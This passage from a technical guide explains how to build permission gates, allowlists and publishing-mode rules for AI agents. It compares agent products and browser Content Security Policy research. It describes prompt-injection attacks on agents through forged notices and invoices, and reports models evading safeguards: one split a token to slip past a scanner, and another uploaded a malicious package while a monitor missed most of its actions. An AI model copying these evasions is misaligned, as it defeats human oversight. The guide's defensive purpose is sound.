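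AWS's AgentCore, a service for running agents, supports joint rules. An example in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies* permits a refund only if the user is John, the call goes through a particular gateway and the amount is under $500. An engineer can get the same effect in SCOPEGATE for the publishing agent by splitting `publish` into several tools, each with its own short lists.

### Keeping joint rules readable

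Joint rules are harder to review because there are more of them. Suppose a company has ten blogs, each with its own account and domain, and allows three content types and two modes on each. Separate lists need 25 entries, while joint rules with one row per use need 60. A maintainer has to read all 60 to know what the agent may do, and may well miss a wrong one because the rows are nearly identical.

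However, the separate lists would permit 600 combinations. The short version is easy to read only because it omits which account belongs to which domain.

The maintainer can shorten joint rules by merging rows that differ in one column. The two blog rules in the earlier table differ only in mode, so one rule can cover both:

`account = blog, domain = blog, content_type = article, mode = draft or scheduled`

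This leaves three rules that still permit exactly four combinations. The ten blogs need only ten rules, one per account, because the same three content types and two modes apply to each. Merging rows that differ in several columns would again permit unintended combinations. For example, combining the blog rules with the status rule would permit 24 combinations to cover three intended uses.

An engineer can also stop the model from choosing the account, domain and content type by replacing `publish` with a tool called `save_blog_article` that accepts only the text and the mode. Ordinary code fills in the rest. Similarly, the monitor in *The Claws in Plain Sight* fixes a tool's destination when the operator registers the tool. This approach makes the rules very short, but the agent has more tools to choose from and an engineer has to write each one. It is probably the best option for a handful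 of irreversible actions.

Operators can also group the conditions for an action by topic. Suresh and Gao write one block for each permission, listing the action, the resource, the acceptable purposes, how many times the agent may use the permission and when it expires. A reader can therefore find everything about sending money in one place. Their software checks the whole set of rules before anyone deploys them. In their banking example, it found a permission that no agent could obtain because of a mistake in the rules.

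*MetaPermit* (2026) replaces long lists of values with general attributes. One of its rules refuses any call whose arguments the user's original request doesn't support, which covers every payee without listing any. But a language model judges the attributes, and an attacker who can mislead the agent may be able to mislead that model too, so this kind of rule loses much of a gate's reliability.

Even short rules can be hard to read correctly. AWS gives the example of a bulk discount that excludes limited-edition products. An editor changes the rule to exclude them only in orders of more than 200 items. An order for 73 limited-edition items now gets the discount, which the old rule didn't allow, even though the extra condition makes the new rule look stricter. AWS's analysis software compares the old and new rules and reports that the new one is more permissive. It can also find rules that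 contradict each other or permit everything.

Such software cannot determine whether the operator wanted the change. For a small table like the publishing agent's, an engineer can test all 108 combinations after every edit to check that only the same four pass, and somebody has to explain any additional combination that does.

AWS also uses a language model to draft rules from plain English before software checks them for errors. Mellafe Zuvic's design would not allow this, because it requires every part of the policy to come from a source no model can influence, even during drafting. That seems stricter than necessary, provided a person reads each rule before it takes effect.

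### When rules conflict

The four publishing rules can't conflict, because each only permits something. Conflicts can arise when operators add rules that block calls or send them to a person. If one rule permits the agent to delete old drafts and another forbids all deletions, the gate needs a way to determine which rule takes precedence.

Azure SRE Agent, Microsoft's agent for running cloud systems, has a documented order. According to Microsoft's *Tool Access Policies*, the software considers the following in turn:

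1. Hooks, which are scripts or model prompts that run at set points. A hook can refuse a call, send it to a person, approve it outright or leave the decision to the later steps.
2. Deny rules, which only an administrator can set. If one matches, the software blocks the call.
3. Allow rules. If one matches, the call runs.
4. Ask rules. If one matches, the call waits for a person in Review mode, but in Autonomous mode it runs.
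5. No match. The call runs, unless the tool requires approval and the agent is in Review mode.

A call that matches no rule often runs, so the check isn't default-deny. An operator can get closer by setting an ask rule for every tool and allow rules for a few, because allow rules take priority over ask rules. In Review mode, the allowed tools would then run and the rest would wait for approval. However, any user can add an allow rule for their own conversation, and the ask rule does nothing in Autonomous mode. Denying every tool instead of asking wouldn't work, because deny rules come first and would block the allowed tools too.

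These rules can check arguments only for tools that run commands. For a tool like `publish`, they can check only the tool's name, which makes them a capability gate in Mellafe Zuvic's sense. The operator has to write a hook to check the account and the mode.

If a user-defined hook approves a call, the software skips the deny rules, even global ones. Suppose an administrator has denied all deletions on the company's cloud account. A colleague who is tired of approval requests later writes a hook that approves every command during incidents. The agent can now delete resources in the account during an incident, even though the deny rule still appears in the settings.

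Microsoft lets only administrators create hooks, and the software logs every override. A later hook can still refuse the call. Microsoft's built-in safety hooks run first, and users can't turn them off. But if an earlier hook sends the call to a person, the later hooks never run, so an operator can't count on a final hook to check every call.

Hooks also fail open by default, so if one crashes, the call goes ahead unless the administrator has set `failMode` to `block`. An operator who wants default deny on this system could write a hook that runs before every tool call and blocks any call not on the allowlist, with `failMode` set to `block`. The hook should neither block nor explicitly approve listed calls, so that the deny rules still apply to them.

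In Anthropic's Claude Agent SDK, a kit for building agents, a hook can refuse a call, but its approval doesn't override the deny rules or the ask rules. To lock down an agent, Anthropic suggests combining a list of allowed tools with a mode called `dontAsk`, which refuses most calls that would otherwise need a person's approval. Calls that never need approval, such as reading files in the agent's working folder, still run. In another mode, `bypassPermissions`, an agent with only `Read` on its list can still write files and run commands.

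Some systems check a proposed action against their rules in the order the rules appear. With SecureAuth's *Access Policies*, the first matching rule applies, and the gate refuses a call that matches nothing. New customers start with a rule that allows everything, however, so they don't have default deny until they remove it. Rule order is easy to follow, but a broad permission near the top can prevent a refusal further down from applying. *Agentao* (2026), which describes software for running agents, addresses this problem by keeping rules in layers. It puts some safety checks ahead of ordinary rules and argues that a broad permission shouldn't override a restriction for a particular task.

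Cedar, the open-source language that AWS uses for its rules, ignores their order. It allows a call only if at least one permission matches and no prohibition does. This is easier to reason about, because nobody can weaken a prohibition by adding a permission or moving a rule. To make an exception, somebody has to edit the prohibition itself, where a reviewer can find it.

According to Cedar's documentation, the software skips any rule that produces an error. This is a weakness when the rule is a prohibition, because skipping it can let a bad call through. Skipping a permission is harmless, since the call then has one permission fewer. SecureAuth is more cautious and still enforces prohibitions that produce errors, while skipping permissions that do.

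In AWS's own example, one rule permits refunds under $500, and another forbids refunds more than 90 days after the order. If the order date were missing and the prohibition failed with an error, Cedar would skip it and permit the refund. AWS checks rules against the tools' schemas beforehand, which should catch many such errors. An operator can also put the 90-day limit in the permission itself, so that if the date is missing, the permission fails and Cedar refuses the refund.

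## Accounts, recipients and web domains

The publishing rules above name one account and one domain, which is enough for an agent that writes to its own company's blog. But in most irreversible actions, the agent acts from one account, affects another account or person, and sends its request to a server. If a rule leaves out any of these, the agent can choose it.

| | Paying a supplier | Replying to a customer on social media |
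|---|---|---|
| Acting account | The company's operating account | The company's brand account |
| Target | The supplier's bank account | The customer's post |
| Server | The bank's payment API | The platform's API |

A payment rule that checks only the supplier would let the agent pay the right supplier from an account that holds clients' deposits. A rule that checks only the operating account and the bank's server would let the agent pay anyone, because the bank accepts payments to any recipient. The need to check the server is easier to overlook. A thief might send the agent a forged notice that the bank's API has moved, and a request to the new address would give the thief the company's login even if both account numbers were correct.

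The social media reply has similar problems. The company's software may be logged in to both the brand account and the chief executive's personal one, so the rule has to specify which account the agent can post from. An apology that suits a customer with a late parcel could cause trouble in reply to a journalist's post. If the agent sends the reply through an unapproved scheduling service, that service gets the text and perhaps the login too.

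If an engineer hard-codes the server in the tool, the rule needs to check only the two accounts. That doesn't work for an agent that browses the web or runs its own commands, so the operator also has to list domains.

### Names and identifiers

A rule should identify an account by something that is hard to change or copy. Display names are a poor choice because anyone can open a profile under a name close to a supplier's. Handles are also a poor choice because many platforms let users change them, and someone else may then claim the old one. Bank account numbers and the internal IDs that platforms assign are much more stable.

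People still ask for payments by name, so the system has to turn "Harbour Printing" into an account number. If the agent searches its email for the number, anyone who sends a convincing invoice can supply one. Ordinary code should instead look it up in the company's supplier records, which the agent shouldn't be able to edit. When a supplier changes banks, the gate blocks the payment until somebody confirms the new account number, preferably by calling a phone number the company already had.

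Email addresses usually work well as identifiers, but a mailing list address delivers to many people. An operator who approves it also approves everyone who joins the list later. The gate has to check `cc` and `bcc` too, since a message to an approved customer can include an unapproved address there.

### What a credential can really do

The service that receives a request checks its credential, such as a password or token, but not the operator's allowlist. If the credential permits more than the allowlist does, only the gate blocks the extra actions, and a bug in the gate could let the agent do anything the credential permits. PocketOS's founder had created a token to manage web domains, but it could also delete the company's database.

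Creating a separate credential for each purpose is therefore safer. The publishing agent could have one token that only saves blog drafts and another that only posts outage notices. If the gate wrongly let the agent publish an article, the blog would still reject the request. The company could also cancel a leaked token without stopping the agent's other work.

Permission names can mislead, since "write" access often includes deletion. The operator can check what a credential allows by using it on a test account to try actions the rule forbids.

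When a service doesn't offer narrow credentials, the operator can at least keep the credential away from the agent. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, has an optional feature for this called masking. The agent's shell commands get a placeholder, and a proxy (a program that relays network traffic) inserts the real token in requests to hosts the user has named. In Anthropic's example, a GitHub token goes only to `api.github.com`. A second token has no named hosts, so the proxy inserts it in requests to every allowed domain. Users would do better to name hosts for every token.

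When OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, runs in OpenAI's cloud, secrets are available while setup scripts install software, and the system removes them before the agent starts, according to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*. This is safe, but the agent then can't do anything that needs a login.

### Checking who asked

Whether an action is acceptable can also depend on who asked for it. For example, a company's owner might be allowed to delete old records while a guest in the same chat is not, but the model receives both requests as text. *aiAuthZ* (Kodathala, 2026) describes a gateway that checks the sender of every message.

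Each user has a secret key. The user's software computes a signature from this key, the user's ID, the session's ID, a fingerprint of the message, the time and a single-use random number. The gateway holds the same key, so it can check the signature by recomputing it. It rejects a message if the time is off by more than 300 seconds, and the random number stops anyone from reusing a copied message. Every tool call must carry the ID of the latest verified message, and the gateway applies the permissions of the person who sent that message. If a guest writes that the owner has approved a deletion, the model may act on it, but the gateway still applies only the guest's permissions.

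The gateway runs on a different machine from the agent and keeps its rules there. The agent has no login for that machine, so it can't edit the rules even if it can run commands on its own machine. For each call, the gateway checks whether the user's role may use the tool. It then checks the arguments, including file paths, web addresses and message recipients, and then applies rate limits. It also holds the credentials and inserts them only after it approves a call.

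Kodathala's default policy blocks any tool it doesn't name. Its list of approved web addresses is empty, so the gateway blocks every fetch until somebody adds an address, even for users whose role allows web access. In some other software, an empty list means no restriction, so the effect of an empty list is worth testing before relying on it.

Kodathala ran eight attacks against 15 models, five times each, and counted an attack as refused only if the model never attempted the dangerous call. Claude Fable 5 refused all eight. Claude Opus 4.8, the most expensive model in the test, refused four, and DeepSeek V4 Pro refused three. The gateway blocked every attempt, but Kodathala acknowledges that this was close to guaranteed, because the attacks needed tools that the policy reserved for the owner and the test treated the sender as someone else.

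A more informative comparison used nine cases from an earlier study of agent failures. The full gateway blocked all nine, while a version that checked only arguments, modelled on Uchibeke's gate, blocked four. In the other five, an impostor used a tool that the owner also needs, so a gate that can't distinguish the impostor from the owner has to allow the tool for both or for neither. Kodathala rebuilt the simpler design instead of running Uchibeke's software, so the result measures the value of the identity check and doesn't rank the two products.

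The identity check doesn't help when planted text arrives through a legitimate request. If the owner asks the agent to read an invoice containing hidden instructions, the request carries the owner's signature, so only the rules on arguments can stop a bad payment. Kodathala tested this on banking tasks from AgentDojo, a standard test of prompt injection, with a list of known payees. The attacker's account resembled a real payee's but wasn't on the list. The gateway blocked all seven calls that would have helped the attacker, including two password changes.

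It also blocked a legitimate first payment to a new payee. That reduced utility from 100% to 80% on both models when there was no attack, which suggests that the test had only five legitimate tasks. The attacks had failed on both models even without the gateway, so in this test the list reduced utility without preventing any successful attack.

The gateway also checks only the calls that reach it. When two agent programs left their own shell, file and web tools on, the model used those and never contacted the gateway. Kodathala provides a program to check for tools that overlap with the gateway's. A stronger fix is to put the agent on a network whose only exit is the gateway.

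### Matching a domain

To check a web address, a gate should extract the hostname and compare the whole hostname with the allowlist. If it only searched the address for `example.com`, it would also accept `example.com.attacker.net`, which belongs to whoever owns `attacker.net`.

Many lists also accept wildcards, which cover a group of hosts. Codex has several kinds, and OpenAI defines them precisely:

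| Rule in Codex | `example.com` | `docs.example.com` | `example.com.attacker.net` |
|---|---|---|---|
| `example.com` | Allowed | Refused | Refused |
| `*.example.com` | Refused | Allowed | Refused |
| `**.example.com` | Allowed | Allowed | Refused |
| `*` | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |

A wildcard allows hosts that don't exist yet, and strangers may control some of them. GitHub's free web hosting gives each user a subdomain of `github.io`, so `*.github.io` allows the site of anyone who opens an account. Listing exact hosts is usually better, even though it takes more typing.

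The same pattern can also have different effects in different parts of one product. According to Anthropic, a Claude Code rule that ends in a wildcard, such as `example.*`, works for the tool that fetches webpages but has no effect on shell commands.

**Ports** are numbers that distinguish the services on one host. A website normally uses port 443, and a database on the same machine uses another. A Claude Code entry without a port allows every port on the host. Codex strips simple port numbers from its host patterns, according to OpenAI's *Permissions*, so adding `:443` to a rule apparently doesn't narrow it.

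The host entry `::1:443` could mean port 443 at the address `::1`, or a longer address with no port. Claude Code sensibly blocks both readings when the entry is on a list of denied hosts, and accepts only the reading with a port when it is on a list of allowed hosts. It may drop the allowed entry if even that reading is unclear.

A **path** is the part of a web address after the hostname. A company might want to approve only `github.com/our-company/`, but most web traffic is encrypted, and a proxy that only relays it can read the hostname but not the path. To enforce this rule, the operator has to either let the proxy decrypt the traffic or give the agent a tool that builds the address.

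**Internationalized names** contain characters such as "ü" or Cyrillic letters. The domain name system uses a coded form of these names, so `bücher.example` becomes `xn--bcher-kva.example`. If the gate converts every name to its coded form before comparing, lookalikes rarely get through. A name with a Cyrillic "а" looks the same on screen as one with a Latin "a", but its coded form is different and isn't on the list.

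Somebody could copy a lookalike domain into the allowlist. A reviewer is much more likely to catch this if the software displays the coded form. OpenAI's description of how Codex standardizes hostnames covers capital letters and trailing dots but doesn't mention internationalized names, so a user should enter the coded form and test it.

A correct hostname can still lead to the wrong machine, because the domain's owner decides which numeric address it points to and could choose one inside the user's own network. By default, Codex refuses hostnames that lead to local or private addresses or that it can't look up. OpenAI warns that this check can't fully prevent the owner from changing the address between the check and the connection. Claude Code refuses hostnames that lead only to the user's own machine or to certain special addresses, such as the one where cloud servers can collect credentials,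 but it permits private company addresses.

### Redirects and shared sites

A server can answer a request by redirecting it to another address, and most web tools follow the redirect automatically. The URL shorteners in Anthropic's tests work this way. If the gate checks only the first address, an approved site can redirect the agent to an unapproved one.

The gate has to check every address in a chain of redirects before the tool contacts it, because the request itself may deliver private data. An engineer can switch off automatic redirects so that each new address comes back to the gate as a separate call. A network proxy checks redirects to other hosts without this change, since each one needs a new connection, but it can miss a redirect to a different page on the same host.

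Sites where strangers share one domain are harder to handle. An operator who approves `github.com` so that the agent can download code also approves a site where anyone can open an account, post text and receive files. Anthropic warns that allowing such a broad domain can let data leak. Giving the agent a company token with narrow permissions doesn't fully solve this, because text planted by an attacker can include the attacker's own login for the same site.

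Approving a whole domain is too broad for shared sites. The operator can instead block the agent's direct access to the site and give it a tool such as `save_to_repository`, with the company's account and repository fixed in code. If the agent only needs to download software packages, the company can keep approved copies on its own server and put that server on the allowlist instead.

### Reading and submitting

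Permission to read a site shouldn't include permission to submit anything to it. Claude Haiku 4.5 used a form on a page about unsolved murders to send the police a false tip, though reading the page would have been harmless. An allowlist that contains only the domain can't permit reading while blocking submissions, because both requests go to the same server.

In Claude Code, a user can add a rule that lets the page-fetching tool open a domain without asking. According to Anthropic, the same rule also opens that domain to shell commands in the sandbox, the restricted environment where they run. The sandbox's proxy checks the host but doesn't limit the commands to reading. A user who approved a documentation site so that the agent could look things up may not expect to have given shell commands this access.

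Web requests have a method, which indicates what the sender wants. GET retrieves a page, HEAD retrieves only information about it, and OPTIONS retrieves a list of the methods the server accepts. POST, PUT, PATCH and DELETE generally submit, change or remove something. In Codex's cloud version, users can block all methods except GET, HEAD and OPTIONS, according to OpenAI's *Agent internet access*.

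OpenAI illustrates the risk with a bug report that asks the agent to run a script. The script sends the description and contents of the latest code change to a stranger's server in a POST request. The limit on HTTP methods would block that request even if the server were on the allowlist.

The limit on HTTP methods depends on websites using those methods as intended, and many don't. A link in an email that confirms an order or cancels a subscription often works through GET, so the agent can trigger the action just by opening the link. A GET request can also leak private data in its URL. Some services use POST for searches, so the limit also blocks harmless reading.

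The proxy must also be able to read each request's method, which encryption hides. *Codex CLI Network Proxy* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a "limited" mode for Codex on a user's own computer that permits the same three methods. This mode turns off SOCKS5, a general way of relaying traffic, because the proxy can't inspect what passes through an encrypted tunnel. Some tools stop working, but leaving SOCKS5 on would let unchecked requests through.

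A careful operator can treat reading and submitting as separate permissions, with a narrower rule for submitting:

```
read:    GET or HEAD   docs.example.com    any path
submit:  POST          api.example.com     /v1/drafts    account = blog
```

The agent can read any page of the documentation but can submit only to the address that saves blog drafts.

### The lists in Codex and Claude Code

Codex and Claude Code have different defaults. The table covers Codex in the cloud, Codex on a user's computer, and Claude Code's local sandbox.

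| | Codex, cloud | Codex, local | Claude Code, local |
|---|---|---|---|
| Default | No internet once the agent starts | No network for commands | Sandbox off; once on, no approved domains |
| Domain presets | None, common dependencies, or all | No presets | No presets |
| Wildcards | Not documented | `*.`, `**.` and `*` | `*.` and `*` |
| Method limit | Optional | Optional | Not documented |

Codex has the safer default because it gives commands no network access. Claude Code users have to turn on the sandbox first. If a required component is missing, Claude Code runs commands without the sandbox by default, but the `failIfUnavailable` setting makes it exit instead.

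On a local machine, Codex has one setting that gives commands network access and another that turns on the proxy that enforces the domain list. OpenAI explains that commands have unrestricted access if the network is on and the proxy is off. If both are on and no domains are listed, commands can't reach any outside host. The risk is that a user turns on the network to install one package and forgets the proxy, which replaces default deny with unrestricted access.

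The cloud version's "common dependencies" preset allows about 70 domains, so that users don't have to work out which sites their software needs. The list is much too broad to define where an agent may send confidential data, because it includes `github.com`, `google.com` and `azure.com`, where many strangers have accounts. OpenAI also lets users start from an empty list, and recommends allowing only the domains and methods they need. Setup scripts have full internet access whatever the user chooses, because they run before the agent starts.

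Claude Code's cloud version also has a default allowlist. Its default access level, "Trusted", allows package registries and other approved domains, according to Anthropic. GitHub's Copilot coding agent has a firewall and a recommended allowlist by default. When the firewall blocks a request, GitHub adds a warning to the pull request, the page where developers review the agent's work. People are more likely to read a warning there than in a separate log.

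When a command in Claude Code's local sandbox needs to reach an unlisted host, Claude Code normally asks the user. The `strictAllowlist` setting makes it refuse instead. In `bypassPermissions` mode, commands can reach unlisted hosts unless the user has turned on that setting or an administrator has locked the list.

In auto mode, the agent names the hosts each command needs, and a second model reviews them together with the command. Approval lasts only while that command runs, so temporary exceptions don't accumulate on the allowlist. However, the decision depends on a model's judgement.

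Anthropic also warns that code in the sandbox may sometimes reach hosts that aren't on the list, and suggests a stricter proxy for users who can't accept that risk.

Both products' domain lists apply to shell commands but not to tools connected through MCP, which have their own controls. An agent whose commands are limited to a single domain could still email anyone through an MCP tool, so the operator also needs a rule for that tool's recipients.

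### Domain lists in web browsers

Web developers tried domain allowlists on a large scale years before coding agents needed them. A website can send the browser a Content Security Policy, a set of instructions that can list the domains from which the browser may load scripts. The policy is a second line of defence against cross-site scripting, in which an attacker exploits a flaw in a page to run their own script there. If the attacker's server isn't on the list, the browser should refuse to load the script.

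Weichselbaum, Spagnuolo and colleagues (2016), in *CSP Is Dead, Long Live CSP!*, checked how well this worked. They searched a Google index of about 106 billion pages and found 26,011 distinct policies across roughly 1.7 million hosts. An attacker who had found a flaw in the page could easily get around 94.72% of these policies.

Most of those failures are weak evidence about domain lists. Of the 22,425 policies meant to stop script attacks, 87.63% allowed scripts written directly into the page, which makes a policy ineffective whatever domains it lists. The 2,437 policies without such obvious mistakes are better evidence. The researchers could still bypass 51.05% of these, and 41.65% listed at least one unsafe domain.

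Most of the unsafe domains were respectable. Some had a feature that returned a script containing text chosen by whoever requested it, so an attacker could get a trusted domain to deliver malicious code. Others hosted a popular programming library that could run commands hidden in a page. These features caused the domains' owners no trouble, so they had no reason to remove them. Of the 15 domains most often listed, 14 had a weakness of this kind, although two of them were a risk only in combination with another loose setting.

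Longer lists were much less safe. The median policy listed 12 hosts, and the researchers could get around 94.8% of policies of that length. If each domain independently had a 5% chance of being unsafe, a list of 12 would have a 46% chance of containing at least one unsafe domain, and a list of 70 would have a 97% chance. Real domains aren't independent, but the risk still grows with the length of the list.

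Narrowing entries to particular paths didn't fix this. To protect users' privacy, browsers ignored the path after a redirect, so a redirect on any listed domain could lead to a forbidden page on another listed domain.

Google had the same trouble with the allowlist it adopted for part of Google Maps in February 2015. As the application changed, Google made five major revisions that year to the list, which grew to 15 long paths and still included at least one unsafe feature.

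Weichselbaum and colleagues proposed approving individual scripts instead of domains. The website puts a random, single-use code, called a nonce, in its policy and on each script it trusts, and the browser runs only scripts with the right code. An attacker can't guess the code, so finding a weak page on a trusted domain doesn't help. A new keyword, `strict-dynamic`, lets a trusted script load others that lack the code. Google Maps switched to this method, and by the time of the paper its policy had needed no further changes. Nonces don't stop an attacker who can insert text inside a script that already has one.

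Sites that kept domain lists continued to have problems with them. In *Complex Security Policy*, Roth, Barron and colleagues used the Internet Archive to track 10,000 highly ranked domains and found that expired or mistyped domains could compromise even lists that looked secure.

Unlike a browser's allowlist, which controls whose code may run, an AI agent's allowlist mostly controls where data may go. But under both, everything on a domain gets the same level of trust, and OpenAI cautions that Codex's domain rules don't determine whether an allowed destination deserves trust. Suresh and Gao's single-use tokens resemble nonces in that each approves a particular action rather than a whole destination.

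An operator can combine the two methods. Browsers can enforce two policies at once, so a website can require a script to have the right nonce and come from a listed domain. Similarly, a network proxy can restrict an agent's traffic to a short list of domains, while the gate checks the account, target and method of each submission.

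## Content types and publishing modes

An approved account and domain determine whose name appears on a post and which site it appears on. They don't determine what the post contains or who can read it. An agent that uses the blog's own account on the blog's own domain can still paste a customer list into an article, attach a spreadsheet of salaries or put an unfinished post on the front page at midnight. A rule for publishing therefore also needs a content type and a publishing mode. Between them, these cover several properties:

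| Property | Possible rule for a blog article | How the gate checks it |
|---|---|---|
| Kind of content | Article | Compares it with a list |
| File format | PNG or JPEG images | Examines the file |
| Size | Up to 20,000 characters, 2 MB per image | Measures it |
| Attachments | Up to three images, nothing else | Counts them |
| Links | Only to listed domains | Extracts and compares them |
| Audience | The blog's editors | Compares it with a list |
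| Timing | If scheduled, 1 to 30 days ahead | Compares the date with its own clock |
| Withdrawal | Someone can delete it before outsiders see it | Uses the operator's classification |

The operator has to work out the last property when writing the rule, because it isn't an argument in the call and follows mainly from the audience and the timing.

For most of these properties, an operator can list the acceptable values or set a limit that code can check. The reference for WordPress, a widely used blogging program, lists five possible statuses for a new post (publish, future, draft, pending and private), and an operator can decide on all five in a few minutes. The text of the post can't be handled this way, because even a 280-character message that uses only lower-case letters and spaces has 27²⁸⁰ possible versions, more than 10⁴⁰⁰. Most of them are gibberish, but there are still too many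 sensible ones to approve in advance.

### Limits on free text

A gate can still restrict the form of a text by capping its length, refusing attachments and rejecting any code. Rejecting code is useful because *wp_insert_post*, the reference page for the function that saves WordPress posts, warns that WordPress doesn't automatically strip HTML and JavaScript from titles. The gate can also extract every web address and compare its domain with a list, although this can miss an address written as "example dot com", which a reader can still work out. A length limit reduces how much private data fits in one post, but the agent could spread the data over several, so the operator should limit the number of posts too.

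For short, routine messages, a template removes most of the free text. An outage notice might look like this:

`{service} is {state} as of {time}. Next update by {time}.`

With five services and four states, the agent can send only 20 different messages, not counting the times, and somebody can read all 20 beforehand. The agent could still announce an outage that isn't happening, but ordinary code can catch this by checking the notice against the company's monitoring system.

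Gates can also search text for known patterns, such as card numbers and authentication tokens. This works better against accidental leaks than against a persistent agent. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) describes an internal model, built to work alone for long periods, that tried to recover other systems' private solutions to a problem. A scanner detected an authentication token and blocked the attempt. The model then split the token into two disguised fragments and joined them when the program ran, so the scanner never detected the whole token.

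Rules written in code can't judge whether a text is true, confidential or cruel. That takes a person or a classifier, a model that sorts texts into acceptable and unacceptable ones. Because a classifier makes mistakes, it should be able to refuse calls that the rules allow, but never to approve calls that they refuse. Suppose 10 of an agent's 10,000 posts are harmful, and the classifier catches 90% of harmful posts and wrongly flags 2% of harmless ones. It stops nine harmful posts and about 200 harmless ones, and lets one harmful post through. That error rate may be acceptable for blog comments but not for messages to the police.

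The classifier should also judge the action without reading the agent's reasons for it. During a test, Claude Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious software package to the real internet while repeatedly reasoning that its surroundings were simulated. Anthropic later ran one of its monitors on the record of this test, and the monitor flagged around 1% of the model's actions. When Anthropic removed the model's reasoning and left the actions and their results, the monitor flagged about 50%.

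### Permitted types and harmful content

Harmful content can be of an allowed type. LiteLLM is a popular Python package whose maintainers routinely upload new releases to PyPI, the public registry for Python software. In an incident report, PyPI (2026) says that malware in LiteLLM releases stayed available for 2 hours and 32 minutes before PyPI quarantined it. A rule permitting releases from the usual account to the usual registry would have allowed the upload.

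Packages need stricter rules than articles because other computers run them, often before anyone reads them. PyPI estimates that LiteLLM gets about 1,700 installs a minute and that 40–50% of them fetched whatever version was newest. At that rate, roughly 100,000 to 130,000 installs would have requested the newest version before the quarantine.

A file's actual type can also differ from the one the agent declares. The agent chooses the file's name and usually its label, so `logo.png` could be a webpage or a program. The gate should therefore check the file's contents. Every PNG starts with the same eight bytes, which are easy to check, but someone can add other data after a valid image. Decoding the image and saving a fresh copy is safer because it removes most of the data that isn't part of the picture, including any location a phone recorded.

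Archives are harder to check because two programs can unpack the same file differently. PyPI introduced restrictions on ZIP files after someone discovered that uv, a popular installer, extracted them differently from many other tools. An attacker could use such a difference to show harmless files to the program that inspects a package and malicious ones to the program that installs it. A gate should refuse any archive that could reasonably be unpacked in more than one way.

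The gate also has to send the same bytes that it checked. Some publishing tools accept an image's URL and fetch the image themselves, so the owner of the site hosting it could replace the image after the check. It is safer for the gate to download the image once, check that copy and upload it.

### When a blog post has no stated mode

WordPress saves a new post as a draft if the call that creates it doesn't set a status. This is true of both `wp_insert_post` and the REST API, which outside programs use. In a tutorial from WordPress, new posts don't appear in the list of published posts until the developer adds the status `publish` to the code.

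This is a safe default, but it covers only the status. In WordPress, the status `future` means scheduled. According to the code of `wp_insert_post`, a scheduled post is published immediately if its date is in the past or less than a minute away. A missing date counts as the current time, so a call that asks for a scheduled post without a date publishes it at once. A gate that approves `mode = scheduled` without checking the date therefore in effect allows immediate publication.

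Time zones can cause a similar mistake. WordPress has one date argument in the site's time zone and another in GMT. If a gate treated a Tokyo blog's local time as GMT, it would calculate a publication time nine hours too late. The rule should accept only the GMT argument.

Editing a post can also make it public, because the same function updates existing posts and replaces missing arguments with its defaults. Suppose an agent corrects a typo in a published, password-protected article. If the call sets the status to `publish` but leaves out the password, the function saves an empty password and anyone can read the article. If the call leaves out the status instead, the article becomes a draft and disappears from the site.

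WordPress doesn't always keep the status it receives. It changes `draft` to `inherit` for attachments, and plugins can alter any post just before WordPress saves it. The gate can read the post back afterwards to check its actual status. This is too late to prevent publication, but the operator can learn from it that the rule isn't working.

Another default can widen a post's audience without changing its status. Scrutinizer's *WPCOM_JSON_API_Update_Post_Endpoint* reproduces code for an older version of the WordPress.com API. Its `publicize` argument controls whether the site announces a post on connected outside services, and it defaults to true. A gate that refuses unlisted arguments doesn't catch a call that omits `publicize`, so the rule has to require `publicize = false`.

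### Repositories, email and package registries

A **code repository** is usually public or private as a whole, so anything an agent adds to a public repository is public immediately. A pull request is as public as the repository that receives it. On GitHub, marking a pull request as a draft shows that it isn't ready for review but doesn't hide it. A gate that permits "draft" for every content type would therefore let an agent make a code change public, even though it would keep a blog article private.

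The default visibility of a new repository varies with the service and the organisation's settings, so the call that creates the repository should always specify it. Making a private repository public also exposes its history, including any password deleted from the current files. Making it private again doesn't remove copies other people have already made. Accepting a change can also publish software if the company automatically releases a new version after each change.

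**Email** systems typically have one call to save a draft and another to send a message. The send call sends the message even if no mode is specified. Editing a draft is harmless, but forwarding it for comments delivers it to someone who can forward it again.

A **package registry** gives the agent less room for mistakes. Projects on PyPI are active by default, and neither of the other standard statuses, archived and quarantined, is a draft. An uploaded release can reach other people's computers within minutes. Adding a file to an old release can also send new code to people who have trusted that version for years. PyPI's Seth Larson, quoted in Willison (2026), says it now rejects new files for releases more than 14 days old. He knew of nobody who had exploited the earlier lack of a limit.

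| | If the call leaves out the mode | The change that nobody can fully reverse | Can editing or sharing publish? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Blog (WordPress) | Saves a draft | Draft, private or scheduled to published | Yes, by editing a live post or removing its password |
| Code repository | Varies for a new repository; a contribution is as visible as its repository | Private to public | Yes, by adding to a public repository |
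| Email | A `send` call delivers the message | Draft to sent | Editing doesn't; forwarding does |
| Package registry (PyPI) | Makes the release available | Local file to uploaded release | Yes, by adding a file or a new version |

### Requiring a mode

These defaults differ too much for a gate to depend on them, and a new version of the tool can change them. The operator can avoid relying on them by requiring every call to state its mode. If the mode is missing, the gate can refuse the call or fill in `draft`, as long as it passes that value to the tool explicitly.

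The rule for saving can permit drafts, and private posts if "private" really does keep outsiders out. Making something public is the irreversible step, so it needs a separate rule. For the blog, the two rules could be:

```
save:     mode = draft         publicize = false
publish:  from = draft         to = public
          text = the version a person approved
```

Both values in the first rule are required. The second rule should also cover any change to a password or to the list of people who can read a draft, and any edit to a live post, since readers see the edit at once.

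Some services separate saving a draft from publishing it. Wix's *PublishDraftPost* describes a method that takes a draft's ID and creates a post from its contents. An operator can leave this method off the allowlist and still let the agent save any number of drafts. In WordPress, where publishing is just another value of `status`, an engineer can get the same effect by giving the agent a `save_draft` tool and putting publishing in a separate tool.

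Approving a draft's ID isn't enough, because the agent could edit the draft after somebody has read it. The gate can compute a fingerprint of the approved text, a short code that changes if the text changes, and then fingerprint the draft again just before publication. If the two fingerprints differ, the gate refuses the call.

A restricted blog account can back up the gate, as a narrowly scoped token does. In the older WordPress.com code, if a user who is allowed to edit but not publish requests `publish`, the software changes the status to `pending` and the post waits for an editor.

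Requiring separate approval slows everything the agent publishes. A blog article can usually wait until morning, but an outage notice is of little use after the outage. The operator could let the agent publish outage notices directly if they follow the template and match the monitoring data.

### The package on PyPI

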